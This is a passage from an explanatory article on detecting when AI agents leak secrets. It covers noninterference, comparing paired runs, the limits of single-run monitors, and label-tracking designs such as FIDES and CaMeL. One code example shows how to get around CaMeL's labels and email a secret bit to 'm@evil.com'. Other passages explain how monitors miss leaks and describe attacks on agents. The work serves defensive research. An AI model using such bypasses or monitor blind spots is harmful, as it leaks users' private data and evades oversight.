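# Checking whether an AI agent leaks secrets by comparing multiple bounded runs

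## What does it mean for an agent to leak a secret?

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop. It reads its inputs, calls a tool such as a calendar or a mail program, reads the result, and repeats until it finishes or is stopped. People give agents access to their mail, diaries and files and let them write to other people, so an agent often holds information that the recipient of a message must not learn. The agent leaks that information if the behaviour the recipient can see depends on it. This can happen without the secret appearing in any message, so searching the messages for it can miss the leak. An alternative is to run the agent several times, changing only the secret between runs, stop each run after a fixed number of steps, and compare what the recipient would have seen. The theory behind this comparison grew out of work on operating systems and compilers in the 1970s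 and 1980s.

### Runs, inputs and observers

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), a study of privacy leaks, describes agents as systems that plan a sequence of actions, carry it out with external tools and adapt the plan to what they observe. A run is one execution of an agent on one task, including everything the agent reads, does and sends. A run is bounded if it ends after at most a fixed number of steps, whether or not the agent has finished.

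Each run has secret inputs, which an observer must not learn about, and public inputs, which the observer may know. Security researchers usually call these "high" and "low" inputs. The lecture notes *Runtime Verification* (2026) model the observer as a function that goes through a run step by step and deletes whatever the observer cannot see. Two runs are indistinguishable if the function leaves the same result for both. In the notes, an invisible step leaves a blank, so the observer can still count steps. Dropping the blanks would model a weaker observer that cannot count the invisible steps.

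The same agent can therefore leak a secret to one observer but not to another. A colleague who receives an e-mail from the agent sees only that e-mail, but the company that runs a search tool sees every query the agent sends it, including queries that never influence the e-mail. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) applies this kind of definition to language-model agents and counts the agent's requests to any tool the attacker can watch as observations.

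### Copying a secret and acting on it

In the simplest kind of leak, the agent copies the secret into its output. *Beyond Data Privacy* (2025), a survey of privacy risks, gives the example of an assistant that drafts an e-mail to John's manager and mentions that John is talking to other companies about a new job. This is an explicit flow, in which the secret, or something computed from it, goes directly into an output.

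In an implicit flow the secret decides which action happens, and the action gives the secret away. Denning and Denning (1977), in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, show it with two statements, where x is a secret that is either 0 or 1:

`y := 1; if x = 0 then y := 0`

Afterwards y equals x, although no instruction copies x into y. Even when x is 1 and the second assignment does not run, y still reveals the secret. Denning had already made this point about untaken branches in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. It applies directly to agents, because a message that an agent did not send, but would have sent under a different secret, can be as informative as one it did send.

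Language models produce implicit flows even without an attacker. In *Can You Keep a Secret?*, Holtzman and West (2026) gave models a secret word, told them not to mention it or hint at it, and asked for a short story. The word never appeared in a story, but one story whose secret was "lighthouse" had an old man climbing a spiral staircase to polish a great lens. A reader model then saw two stories written with different secrets and had to pick the one that matched a given word. Random guessing would succeed half the time. For five of the seven story-writing models, the reader was right 64% to 79% of the time.

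Under a stronger instruction to avoid every theme or image associated with the word, most models wrote so far away from their secret that the reader did worse than chance. With Claude Opus 4.6's stories, the reader was right only 25% of the time. The secret still shaped these stories, so anyone who reversed the reader's answers would have been right 75% of the time.

Holtzman and West attribute the effect to the many small choices that writing a story requires, each of which the secret can influence. Similarly, a secret can influence which of several equally good methods an agent uses to do its job.

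### The scheduling assistant

*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) provides the example used in the rest of the discussion. A user asks a scheduling assistant to find a time for a team meeting and allows it to share which slots are free. The assistant can read the whole calendar, so it also knows why each busy slot is busy, but it must not reveal those reasons. The observer is a colleague who receives the proposal.

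Suppose two versions of a calendar have the same free slots, including 10 and 11, and the same busy slots. One busy slot holds an ordinary meeting in the first version and a confidential interview in the second. The assistant offers slot 10 in the first case and slot 11 in the second. Both proposals are correct and neither mentions an interview, but a colleague who knows this pattern can tell from the offered slot whether an interview is scheduled.

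An agent can leak a secret without bad intent. Pandey et al. note that such a dependence could be a harmless way of breaking ties, a deliberate signal, or the result of an instruction somebody planted in the agent's input. The colleague learns the same thing in each case.

### Noninterference

Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, introduced the property that rules this out. Their setting is a machine that several users share. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does with certain commands affects what the second group sees. To make that exact, let $w$ be any sequence of commands that the users issue, let $w_{-G}$ be the same sequence without the commands of group $G$, and let $\mathrm{out}_u(w)$ be what user $u$ sees at the end. Then $G$ does not interfere with the second group if, for every $w$ and every $u$ in that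 group,

$$\mathrm{out}_u(w) = \mathrm{out}_u(w_{-G}).$$

This version hides the fact that somebody issued a command. Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, contrast it with the version usual in work on programming languages, which hides the value of some data. The second fits agents better, because their secrets are mostly things they read. It compares two runs. Write $T$ for the set of all runs the agent can produce, $\mathrm{low}(t)$ for the public input of run $t$, and $\mathrm{obs}(t)$ for what the observer sees of it. Noninterference is then the requirement that, for all $t$ and $t'$ in $T$,

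$$\mathrm{low}(t) = \mathrm{low}(t') \;\Rightarrow\; \mathrm{obs}(t) = \mathrm{obs}(t').$$

Noninterference means that changing only the secret input changes nothing the observer sees. We must decide separately how to treat runs that never finish. A common variant, termination-insensitive noninterference, compares only pairs of runs that both finish.

Noninterference is stricter than a guessing test because it fails whenever the secret affects the output, even if a particular reader can't use the difference to guess the secret. Holtzman and West also asked their models for short jokes, and the reader model's score stayed close to 50%, which they count as no leak. But Claude Opus 4.6 told one stock joke for 11 of the 15 secret words and another joke for the other four. If that split is stable, someone who knows about it and hears the second joke can narrow the 15 words down to four. The reader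 model had no way to know about the split.

### Permitted release

Taken literally, the formula would forbid the assistant from doing its job. Suppose slot 10 is free in one calendar and taken in another. Any competent assistant makes different proposals in the two cases, and the colleague sees the difference. Since the whole calendar is secret input, this counts as interference. Most useful programs have the same problem. Sabelfeld and Sands mention a program that publishes the average of a set of secret salaries, and a login screen, which reveals that a guess was wrong when it rejects a password.

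The remedy is to specify which part of the secret may be released and require noninterference for the rest. This is called declassification or, more plainly, "permitted release". In the simplest case that Sabelfeld and Sands discuss, the secret is a whole number and the policy permits the release of its parity (whether it is odd or even). Any two secrets with the same parity must then lead to the same visible result. For example, an observer must see the same result for 4 and 10 but may see different results for 4 and 7.

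Pandey and colleagues write the general form with two functions that come from the policy. $D$ takes the secret input $\mathrm{hi}(t)$ and returns the part that the agent may release. The projection $\alpha$ takes everything the observer sees and returns the part that the check compares. For all runs $t$ and $t'$:

$$\mathrm{low}(t) = \mathrm{low}(t') \,\wedge\, D(\mathrm{hi}(t)) = D(\mathrm{hi}(t')) \;\Rightarrow\; \alpha(\mathrm{obs}(t)) = \alpha(\mathrm{obs}(t')).$$

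For the scheduling assistant, $D$ returns whether each slot is free or busy and omits the reasons. The projection keeps the slots offered, any reason or label attached to them, the level of detail and the recipient, but drops the wording of the greeting. Two calendars with different free slots are no longer a fair comparison, so the assistant may treat them differently. The calendars with the ordinary meeting and the interview are a fair comparison because $D$ returns the same result for both, and the assistant fails on this pair.

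If $D$ returns nothing, the formula is ordinary noninterference apart from the projection. If $D$ returns the entire secret, the formula compares only runs with identical secrets. A deterministic agent, which always does the same thing on the same input, then passes no matter what it reveals.

A policy can come close to that second extreme by accident. Sabelfeld and Sands point out that if a policy permits the release of a password's hash, a scrambled code computed from the password, a program may pass this type of check while printing the password itself. When no two passwords share a hash, two secrets that agree on the permitted part are the same secret, so the check has no different secrets to compare. The scheduling policy would have this defect if it let the assistant share a unique code computed from each calendar entry, including the reason.

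Sabelfeld and Sands also warn about policies that specify what may be released but not who chooses it. If a shop may log any four digits of a credit card number, an attacker who controls the choice can request different digits at each purchase and collect the whole number. Pandey and colleagues concede that choosing $D$ and $\alpha$ well takes human judgement. Any mistake in that choice carries over to the test.

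### Why two runs can settle the matter

Noninterference is a hyperproperty, whereas most rules that people set for software are trace properties. Clarkson and Schneider (2009) drew this distinction in *Hyperproperties*. A trace property is a set of acceptable runs, and a system satisfies it if every run the system can produce belongs to the set. "Never write to the network after reading a file" is a trace property, since each run either obeys it or does not. A hyperproperty is a set of acceptable sets of runs, and a system satisfies it if the full set of runs it can produce is one of them. "The mean response time over all runs stays below one second" is a hyperproperty, because one slow run is acceptable if enough of the others are fast. Likewise, under noninterference, whether the assistant may offer slot 11 depends on what it offers in other runs.

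Hyperproperties vary in how easily a tester can refute them. No finite batch of slow runs refutes the rule about mean response time, since later runs may bring the mean back down. For other hyperproperties, a finite set of runs can establish a violation that no later run can undo. Clarkson and Schneider call a hyperproperty k-safety if every system that violates it can produce a set of at most k finite runs, possibly only the beginnings of longer ones, that no system satisfying the hyperproperty can produce. In one of their examples, a system splits a secret into k shares and must never output all k over all its runs together. Pandey and colleagues prove that noninterference with permitted release is 2-safety.

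On the scheduling example the proof is easy to follow. Put the two runs side by side:

- The public input is the same, because the user made the same request.
- $D$ gives the same result, because the same slots are free.
- The projection gives different results, slot 10 and slot 11.

These two runs show that the formula is false for this agent. Continuing them or starting new ones can't change that, because these two would still be among the runs the agent can produce. For a deterministic agent, the pair also shows that the hidden reason caused the difference, because nothing else changed. The tester doesn't need statistics or access to the model's internals, only the ability to restart the agent. Clarkson and Schneider give their observer the same ability by letting it reset the system at will.

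A pair of runs that agree is much weaker evidence. It clears the agent for two particular secrets on one particular task.

### When the agent is not deterministic

The argument fails when chance affects the outcome. *Model checking of hyperproperties for high-level relational models* (Macedo and Pacheco, 2025) shows this with a model of a conference system in which a reviewer must learn nothing about papers that other people review. When the editor always takes the most favourable verdict from a paper's reviewers, noninterference holds for every case within the size limits of the check. When the editor may take any of the submitted verdicts, the checking software immediately finds two runs with the same public input and different decisions. The editor consulted no secret in either run, and the decisions differ because the editor's choice was arbitrary.

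Most agents are random, like the second editor. A language model normally draws each next word at random from a distribution, and *AgentSecBench* (2026) accordingly defines an agent as a randomised map from inputs to outputs. If the scheduling assistant picks between slots 10 and 11 by something like a coin toss, two runs will often differ even when the calendar is the same. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* (2026) separates deterministic from randomised servers for a closely related property of agent benchmarks. One pair of runs can prove a violation on a deterministic server, but if the server is randomised, the property requires only equal distributions, so showing a violation takes statistics. The matching requirement for secrets is probabilistic noninterference, which means that changing the secret must not change the probability of anything the observer may see.

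Leaks then come in sizes, and total variation distance measures them. Let $P$ be the distribution of what the observer sees under one secret and $Q$ the distribution under another. The distance is the largest gap between the probabilities that the two give to the same event $A$:

$$\mathrm{TV}(P, Q) = \max_A \, |P(A) - Q(A)|.$$

Suppose the assistant offers slot 10 in 55% of runs when the hidden reason is an ordinary meeting and in 50% when it is an interview, and offers slot 11 in the rest. The probabilities differ by 0.05 for each slot, so the distance is 0.05. The deterministic assistant, which always offers slot 10 in one case and slot 11 in the other, has distance 1. An assistant satisfies probabilistic noninterference when the distance is 0.

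The distance also limits how accurately an observer can guess the secret from a single run. *The Oversight Gap* (2026) bounds a guesser's accuracy, averaged over the two cases, at one half plus half the distance, which is 52.5% here. The colleague reaches this bound by guessing "ordinary meeting" on seeing slot 10 and "interview" on seeing slot 11, which is right 55% of the time in the first case and 50% in the second.

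Few people would require a language model to have a distance of exactly zero. *PACE* (2026), a design for controlling agents' tool calls, uses probabilistic noninterference as a reference standard and lets an observer distinguish two secrets by up to a margin δ. Under total variation distance, the assistant in the example passes at δ = 0.1 but fails at δ = 0.01.

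## Why is reading a single run not enough?

Most safeguards for agents look at one run at a time. A monitor, which may be a program, a language model or a person, watches the agent and decides whether to stop it. Pandey and colleagues surveyed the published designs of six such safeguards, from asking a human to approve each tool call to tracking every piece of data, and found none that compares two runs. They also proved that no monitor that sees only one run can detect leaks like the scheduling assistant's without raising false alarms.

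### The argument

The proof rests on the fact that noninterference with permitted release only ever compares one run with another.

1. Take any run and imagine an agent that can produce only this run. The only comparison left is between the run and itself. A run always looks the same as itself, so this agent satisfies the property.
2. A monitor that reads only this run cannot tell whether it came from the compliant agent or from a leaking one. If it raises an alarm, the alarm is false for the compliant agent. A monitor that never raises a false alarm must therefore let the run pass.
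3. The same reasoning applies to every run, so the monitor lets all of them pass, including both runs of a leaking pair.

A single run can't show whether the assistant's output depends on a secret, however capable the monitor is and however much of the run it sees. Suppose the monitor reads the whole calendar, finds the confidential interview and sees the assistant offer slot 11. An assistant that always offers slot 11 would have produced the same run.

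Under the proof's strict definition, an alarm is false if any compliant agent could have produced the run, however unlikely such an agent is. For example, a proposal might mention the confidential interview. An agent that wrote the same sentence whatever the calendar contained would leak nothing, so a monitor that avoids all false alarms must let the proposal pass. In practice, a separate rule would forbid secret values in messages, and a single-run monitor can enforce that rule. The theorem matters for the remaining leaks, in which each run looks ordinary.

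Pandey and colleagues prove a similar result for random agents when the monitor cannot see the hidden reason for a choice. Suppose one assistant tosses a coin to choose between slots 10 and 11, and another offers slot 11 only when there is an interview. Both sometimes offer slot 11, so a monitor that objects to that offer wrongly accuses the first assistant, and a monitor that stays silent misses the leak by the second.

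This leaves three ways to detect such leaks: accept some false alarms, audit the agent offline on runs with different secrets, or compare runs while the agent is in use. The last two require more than one run.

### Nine judges

Pandey and colleagues also tested language models as monitors. Nine models judged the leaking scheduling run one action at a time. Each model saw ten versions of the scenario, with different slots, hidden reasons and wording, three times each. The table gives the number of trials, out of 30, in which the model objected. In the harmless run the assistant offers the same slot whatever the hidden reason. In the overt violation it obeys a planted instruction to forward information to an outsider.

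| Judge | Leaking run, action by action | Harmless run, action by action | Overt violation | Both leaking runs together |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Kimi-K2.6 | 3 | 1 | 30 | 30 |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 0 | 2 | 30 | 30 |
| Llama-4-Maverick | 0 | 0 | 30 | 17 |
| Six others, including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 | 0 | 0 | 30 | 30 |

Eight of the nine judges never blocked the leaking run. Kimi-K2.6 blocked it three times, but it also blocked a harmless run once, so it was more likely being cautious in general than detecting the leak. All nine judges caught the overt violation every time, so they were not approving everything.

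When the same models saw both runs, eight flagged the leak in all 30 trials, but Llama-4-Maverick flagged it in only 17. The second run exposes the difference, but the judge model still has to detect it and recognize it as a sign of a leak.

The perfect scores in the last column cover only leaking pairs, so a judge that flagged every pair would also score 30. The experiment would be more convincing if the column also included harmless pairs.

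### A ceiling on accuracy

The theorem is all or nothing, while real leaks differ in how much they reveal in a single run. *The Oversight Gap* puts a number on this. Let $P_0$ be the distribution of what the monitor sees when the agent is clean, and $P_1$ the distribution when it leaks. A monitor's balanced accuracy, BA, is the average of two rates: the share of clean runs it approves and the share of leaking runs it blocks. Guessing scores 50%. Every single-run monitor obeys

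$$\mathrm{BA} \le \tfrac{1}{2} + \tfrac{1}{2}\,\mathrm{TV}(P_0, P_1).$$

This is the bound that limited the colleague's guess about the interview, applied now to a monitor guessing whether the agent leaks. The proof is short. Let $A$ be the set of runs the monitor approves. It approves a share $P_0(A)$ of clean runs and blocks a share $1 - P_1(A)$ of leaking ones, so

$$\mathrm{BA} = \tfrac{1}{2}\,[P_0(A) + 1 - P_1(A)] = \tfrac{1}{2} + \tfrac{1}{2}\,[P_0(A) - P_1(A)].$$

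The last bracket is the difference between a single event's probabilities under the two distributions, so it cannot exceed the total variation distance. A monitor reaches this maximum by approving exactly the runs that a clean agent is more likely to produce than a leaking one. Randomizing the decision doesn't help, because a randomized monitor's result is an average of the results of deterministic monitors.

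Suppose half of all calendars contain an interview and the monitor sees only the proposals. The leaking assistant offers slot 11 exactly when there is an interview, and the clean one tosses a coin to decide whether to offer it. Both offer each slot half the time, so the distance is 0 and no monitor can exceed 50% accuracy. By contrast, a leak may put the wrong type of value in an answer, such as the blood group O+ in place of a delivery address. The distance is then 1, and one run is enough for perfect detection.

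Language models can fall far below this ceiling. On leaks of the blood-group type, a 20-line program scored 100%, while nine models averaged 60.9%. Seven of the models were then also told to check whether the value was of the right type for the question, and their average rose from 58.9% to 83.8%. So better instructions can fix some failures of single-run monitors, but not those that occur when the distance is 0.

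### Imagining a second run and executing one

*The Oversight Gap* tests whether a capable model can work out what a second run would look like, so that a monitor wouldn't need one. In the test, an assistant serves several customers. One customer asks for a personal detail, and the assistant states either that customer's value or, if there is a leak, someone else's. Each detail has four equally plausible values, which are assigned to customers at random. A single session therefore holds no clue to whether the value leaked, and a model that reads only that session can do no better than 50%.

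The experiment varied what the monitor knew and whether it had a rule to block the answer if the stated value differed in a second run where only the other customer's data had changed. With one run and no rule, nine models averaged 50.5%. When they had to imagine the second run and apply the rule, they averaged 50.4%.

The improvement came from executing the second run. The average was 65.8% with both real runs but no rule. Adding the rule raised it to 90.0%, with individual models ranging from 70% to 100%.

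The imagined runs were poor substitutes for real ones. The value in an imagined run matched the real value 1.2% of the time, compared with 25% for picking one of the four values at random. The model usually repeated the value it had already seen.

The models in this test, which ranged from Llama-3.1-8B to GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4, were already old when the results appeared in September 2026. Newer models would probably do better with two real runs, as most of the judges in the scheduling experiment did. But they could not exceed 50% with an imagined run, because that ceiling applies to any monitor, however capable.

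A further test suggests that success with pairs of runs doesn't always carry over to other tasks. It covered sycophancy, the tendency to agree with whatever view the user has expressed, which also shows up only when two runs are compared. With both runs and the rule, the average score was 83.9%, but GPT-4o-mini scored 50%, down from the high nineties on the customer data. All these results come from comparing one clearly stated value, which is easier than comparing everything an agent does.

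### Following labels through one run

Label tracking is a serious alternative that needs only one run. It attaches a label to each piece of data, saying who may read it, and passes the label on to anything computed from that data. It uses the first of the three options, accepting false alarms.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system of this type from Microsoft. If one document is labeled as readable by A, B and C, and another by B, C and D, a text that draws on both is labeled as readable only by B and C. A language model's answer gets the combined label of everything in its conversation, because FIDES has no precise way to tell which parts the model used. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) still lists precise label tracking through language models among the open challenges.

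Before each tool call, ordinary code outside the model checks the labels. The agent may send a piece of information only if every recipient has permission to read it.

In the scheduling example, only the user may read the reasons for busy slots. In the simplest version of the system, everything the assistant writes after reading the full calendar is labeled "user only", and the check blocks any proposal to the colleague. This stops the assistant that signals the interview, but it also stops one that always offers the earliest free slot and leaks nothing. The monitor catches the leak by raising false alarms, so it does not contradict the theorem.

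FIDES reduces the damage by hiding restricted data in variables. The planning model receives only a variable's name, which it can pass to other tools, so its conversation keeps a less restrictive label. A second model without tools can read the contents and answer questions about them. A policy may let a yes-or-no answer through because it carries only one bit, but for the scheduling assistant, that bit is enough to reveal whether there is an interview.

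CaMeL, another design, separates planning from data more firmly. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues explain that one model sees only the user's request and trusted descriptions of the tools, and writes a program for the task. A second model handles untrusted data but cannot call tools. An interpreter runs the program and tracks the data from step to step. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends the design, each value carries a record of its sources and permitted readers, and a policy uses that record to allow or deny each tool call.

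### When the secret steers the program

Labels follow data well when one value goes into another. They have more trouble with implicit flows, where the secret decides which action happens.

Costa and colleagues acknowledge that FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Explicit secrecy requires that the secret make no visible difference along any one fixed path through the agent's work, but it ignores what an observer can infer from which path the agent takes. Someone who sees the order of the tool calls may therefore still learn something about the secret. Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property deliberately because, in their view, enforcing full noninterference would amount to forbidding any publicly visible tool call after the agent has called a tool that may read a secret.

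CaMeL does track some implicit flows. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, give the example of a program that sends an e-mail if an account balance exceeds a threshold. CaMeL blocks the e-mail because the condition depends on the balance. The following program, based on a classic example from the 1970s, gets around the check:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
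if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false, so the program skips the fourth line and `rich` stays true. CaMeL raises a variable's label only on a branch that the program takes, so it still treats `rich` as public and allows the e-mail. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no e-mail goes out. The recipient can therefore tell whether the balance is high. Comparing one run with a high balance and one with a low balance would reveal the leak, since only the first sends an e-mail.

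Better tracking can close this gap without a second run. Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents that stops a program when a secret condition would make it write to a conversation still labelled public. They gave a machine-checked proof that every program in the language, including those a model writes while the agent is working, satisfies a form of probabilistic noninterference. The guarantee does not cover leaks through whether a program finishes. That exception also matters for CaMeL, whose retry loop can leak information through whether each attempt succeeds.

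The strongest objection to the argument for comparing runs is that monitoring a single run can guarantee there are no implicit flows, provided the monitor also stops some harmless programs.

### What blocking costs

A label tracker blocks more harmless actions in some tasks than in others. Costa and colleagues measured this on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks, using GPT-4o with no attack under way. A basic agent completed 75.0% of the office tasks without label checks and 37.0% with them. Its score fell from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking and from 93.3% to 20.0% on Slack, but did not fall in travel. Under the same checks, FIDES, with its variables, completed more tasks than the basic agent in the other three areas, with 59.0% in the office, 52.5% in banking and 47.6% on Slack.

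These checks were mainly meant to stop planted instructions, so the figures don't isolate how much keeping secrets reduces task completion. The same is true of the banking test by Garby and colleagues, where CaMeL completed its task in 18 of 48 runs (16 tasks, three runs each) with its policies switched on. Their own agent succeeded about twice as often with enforcement always on, but it could explicitly mark untrusted data as trusted, and it completed fewer tasks without that ability.

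The losses can grow as restricted labels spread through a system, a process called label creep. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated teams of agents in which an agent that touches sensitive data stays restricted from then on. They measured the share of tool calls that introduced sensitive data or happened under a restricted label. That share fell when they used more agents, and when they gave the sensitive tools to only a few agents. But some loss remained even in an ideal layout, where agents passed results directly to whoever needed them. The simulation used no language models, so it shows how labels spread but not how many real tasks would fail.

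Every practical system therefore needs some way to let harmless messages through. The FlowSeal system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* does this with a separate language model that compares each outgoing message with the protected records the agent has read. When the researchers replaced this checker with a rule that blocked every message it would have examined, the agent completed none of its harmless tasks. With the checker, it completed 72.4%, and at most 3.3% of the sensitive items leaked in any attack they tried.

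The checker caught many leaks in which the agent wrote nothing secret. In one attack, an outsider gives the agent a page of true and invented facts about a person and asks it to delete the invented ones, which leaves only the true ones. This exposed 75.6% of the sensitive items under a prompt-based defence and 2.3% under FlowSeal. A checker can confirm that the remaining facts are true by reading the protected records. In the scheduling example, though, a checker could read both the calendar and the offer of slot 11 and still not know whether the assistant would have offered slot 10 if the interview had been an ordinary meeting.

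## How does self-composition turn a two-run property into an ordinary check?

An ordinary verification tool takes one program and one condition, and tries to prove that the condition holds in every run. Noninterference doesn't fit this form because it compares two runs. *Secure Information Flow by Self-Composition* (Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk, 2004) joins two copies of the program into one, so that a single run of the joined program contains a pair of runs of the original.

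### The construction

In this example, the following five lines choose the scheduling assistant's proposal. For now, we treat the list of free slots as public input and the reason a slot is busy as secret.

```
offer = first(free)
backup = second(free)
if reason == "interview":
    offer = backup
send(offer)
```

This is an implicit flow, since the reason never goes into `offer` but decides which slot does. To check the program:

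1. Copy it.
2. Rename the variables so that the copies share no memory.
3. Assume at the start that the public inputs are equal.
4. Assert at the end that the public outputs are equal.

The result is one longer program:

```
assume free1 == free2

offer1 = first(free1)
backup1 = second(free1)
if reason1 == "interview":
    offer1 = backup1

offer2 = first(free2)
backup2 = second(free2)
if reason2 == "interview":
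    offer2 = backup2

assert offer1 == offer2
```

The `assume` line restricts the check to runs where its condition is true. The `assert` line must hold in every run that reaches it. Nothing restricts `reason1` and `reason2`, so the tool has to consider every combination of their values.

The assertion fails when the free slots are 10 and 11, `reason1` is "meeting" and `reason2` is "interview". The first copy leaves `offer1` at 10 and the second sets `offer2` to 11. The tool returns these values as its counterexample, and the two reasons are the secrets that show the leak. If the programmer deletes the `if` and the line under it, both offers depend only on the free slots, and the tool can prove the assertion for all inputs at once.

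For a deterministic program, the assertion fails on a pair of terminating runs exactly when that pair violates noninterference. If either copy loops forever, the program never reaches the assertion, so the check establishes only termination-insensitive noninterference.

This makes self-composition more precise than label tracking. Suppose both branches of an `if` on the reason assign the same slot to the offer. A tracker that follows implicit flows labels the offer as secret because the program assigned it under a secret condition. Self-composition accepts the program because the offers in the two runs are always equal. It also catches the program that got around CaMeL's labels.

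In the real policy, the whole calendar is secret, and $D$ returns which slots are free. To handle permitted release, the first line changes to assume that $D$ gives the same result for both calendars, and the last line changes to compare the projections $\alpha$ of what the observer sees. If the assistant sends several messages, each copy can store its messages in a list, and the assertion compares the lists.

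### Running the copies side by side

Placing one copy after the other is simple, but it often produces a program that automatic tools can't verify. Cheng and Farzan (2025), in *Products of Recursive Programs for Hypersafety Verification*, show why with a function that divides whole numbers by repeated subtraction:

```
def div(n, d):
    if n < d: return 0
    return div(n - d, d) + 1
```

The property to prove is that a larger `n` never gives a smaller result for the same `d`. Like a leak check, it compares two runs, though it doesn't involve secrets.

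If the second call starts after the first has finished, the tool has to rely on a summary of the first call's result. A summary such as "the result is at least zero" is too weak. It has to state that the result is exactly `n` divided by `d`, rounded down. Automatic solvers fail to find this summary, which involves multiplying unknown numbers.

When the two calls run in step, starting with `n1` at most `n2`, each step subtracts `d` from both numbers, so `n1` stays at most `n2`. If the first call stops earlier, it returns 0, which can't exceed the other result. As the calls return, each adds 1 for every step it took. The tool only has to show that one step preserves the order, so it doesn't have to prove that the function performs division.

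The same applies to checking for leaked secrets. Suppose an agent's code loops over 200 e-mails. If the two copies of the code are placed one after the other, the tool must describe everything the loop computes, but if they are side by side, the tool may only need to show that they still agree after each e-mail.

Terauchi and Aiken (2005) proposed such an interleaving in *Secure Information Flow as a Safety Problem*, which also introduced the term "2-safety". Their method first uses a type system to find the parts of a program that depend only on public data. Both copies behave identically there, so the method keeps them together and separates them only where the program's behavior may depend on a secret. In the scheduling program, the copies would stay together for the first two lines and separate at the `if`.

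Later work generalised this to product programs, which can run the copies together in some places and separately in others, or run them at different speeds. If `n1` is twice `n2`, for instance, the first copy of `div` should take two steps for each step of the second. The choice of product affects how hard the proof is, but not whether the property is true.

Cheng and Farzan built a tool, HyRec, that constructs product programs for recursive code from a short description of how to align the program's copies. It solved 98 of 103 test problems. Without product programs, existing solvers handled the arithmetic problems only when a linear formula could describe what the function returns. The user has to supply the alignment, but Cheng and Farzan found the right one easy to guess.

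Alignment does not always help. Two of the five failures involved proving that $n \times m = m \times n$ for a function that multiplies by repeated addition. The two runs add different numbers a different number of times, and none of the alignments that Cheng and Farzan define makes the proof simple enough for a solver.

### Temporal logics for hyperproperties

The assertion in the example compares the two copies once, at the end. An agent that keeps receiving and sending messages needs a rule about every step. Linear temporal logic, LTL, expresses such rules for a single run with words like "always" and "eventually". HyperLTL adds the ability to talk about several runs at once. Noninterference becomes

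$$\forall \pi_1\, \forall \pi_2.\;\; \mathsf{G}\,(\mathrm{low}_{\pi_1} = \mathrm{low}_{\pi_2}) \;\rightarrow\; \mathsf{G}\,(\mathrm{obs}_{\pi_1} = \mathrm{obs}_{\pi_2}),$$

where $\mathsf{G}$ means "at every step". In words, any two runs that agree on public input throughout also look the same to the observer throughout. Self-composition is enough to check this formula. Pacheco (2026), in *OmegaHyper*, notes that standard model checkers, programs that explore all the states a system can reach, can handle any formula that does not mix "for all runs" with "there exists a run".

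Generalised noninterference combines "for all" with "there exists". Gospodinov, Müller and Dardinier (2026), in *Hyper Separation Logic*, define it to mean that for any two runs with the same public input, there is a third run with that input, the first run's secret and the second run's public output. An observer who sees an output then can't rule out any secret, because each secret could have led to it.

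Generalised noninterference is weaker than noninterference and allows harmless arbitrary choices. In Macedo and Pacheco's conference system, an editor who picks freely among a paper's own reviews violates noninterference but satisfies generalised noninterference. If the editor may also base the decision on reviews of other papers, for example to keep to a quota, generalised noninterference fails too.

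Generalised noninterference ignores probabilities, which makes it a poor test for language models. Suppose an assistant offers slot 11 in 90% of runs when there is an interview and in 10% when there isn't, and otherwise offers slot 10. Both offers are possible in both cases, so the assistant satisfies the property. But the total variation distance between the two distributions of offers is 0.8, and a colleague who uses the offer to guess whether there is an interview is right 90% of the time.

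Mixed formulas also take a lot of computation to check. According to Pacheco, AutoHyper is the only complete checker for arbitrary HyperLTL formulas, and it works only on finite-state systems. The computation needed grows extremely fast with the number of switches between "for all" and "there exists", and even one switch limits the tool to small systems.

One of Pacheco's examples is a small program with three threads that compares a decreasing number with a secret three-bit PIN. If the number can start anywhere, it can reach the PIN, and the comparison then affects a public result. The property holds when the number must start below the PIN, because it then never reaches it. Checking the leaking version by listing every state separately takes 9,342 states. Pacheco's improved tool, OmegaHyper, reduces this to 731 by handling the PIN and the choice of thread symbolically. The PIN has only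 eight possible values, far fewer than the possible contents of a calendar.

Other tools give up completeness and search only runs up to a maximum length, so they cannot in general prove that a property holds. Pacheco compared several checkers on 120 published problems and found that these bounded tools still do better than OmegaHyper when the property fails and a short counterexample exists. People can also write proofs by hand. Gospodinov and colleagues extended this approach to mixed properties of programs that allocate memory at run time and access it through pointers, and used a proof assistant to check that their rules are sound.

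### Unrolling the loop

A bounded search fits an agent that stops after a fixed number of steps. *Agentic Model Checking* (2026) describes bounded model checking as deciding whether an execution of at most $k$ steps can violate a property. For ordinary code, tools such as CBMC for C, Kani for Rust and JBMC for Java return either a concrete counterexample or a proof that no violation occurs within the bound.

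The method replaces a loop with $T$ copies of its body, so that no loop remains. Let $s_0, s_1, \ldots, s_T$ be the states of the workflow in a run $t$. The following formula describes a valid run:

$$\mathrm{Run}_T(t) \;=\; \mathrm{Init}(s_0) \,\wedge\, \bigwedge_{i=0}^{T-1} \mathrm{Step}(s_i, s_{i+1}).$$

$\mathrm{Init}$ describes the permitted starting states, and $\mathrm{Step}$ describes what one step may change. *MANTRA* (2026), which checks compliance tests for tool-using agents, shows how to write $\mathrm{Step}$. If the agent calls a tool at step $i$, the tool's preconditions must hold at $i$, and its postconditions restrict the state at $i+1$. For example, a mail tool might require that a draft exists and guarantee that the message is in the sent folder afterwards.

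For a leak, the solver needs two valid runs that agree on everything the policy lets the observer know but look different:

$$\begin{aligned}
&\mathrm{Run}_T(t) \wedge \mathrm{Run}_T(t') \\
&\wedge\; \mathrm{low}(t) = \mathrm{low}(t') \,\wedge\, D(\mathrm{hi}(t)) = D(\mathrm{hi}(t')) \\
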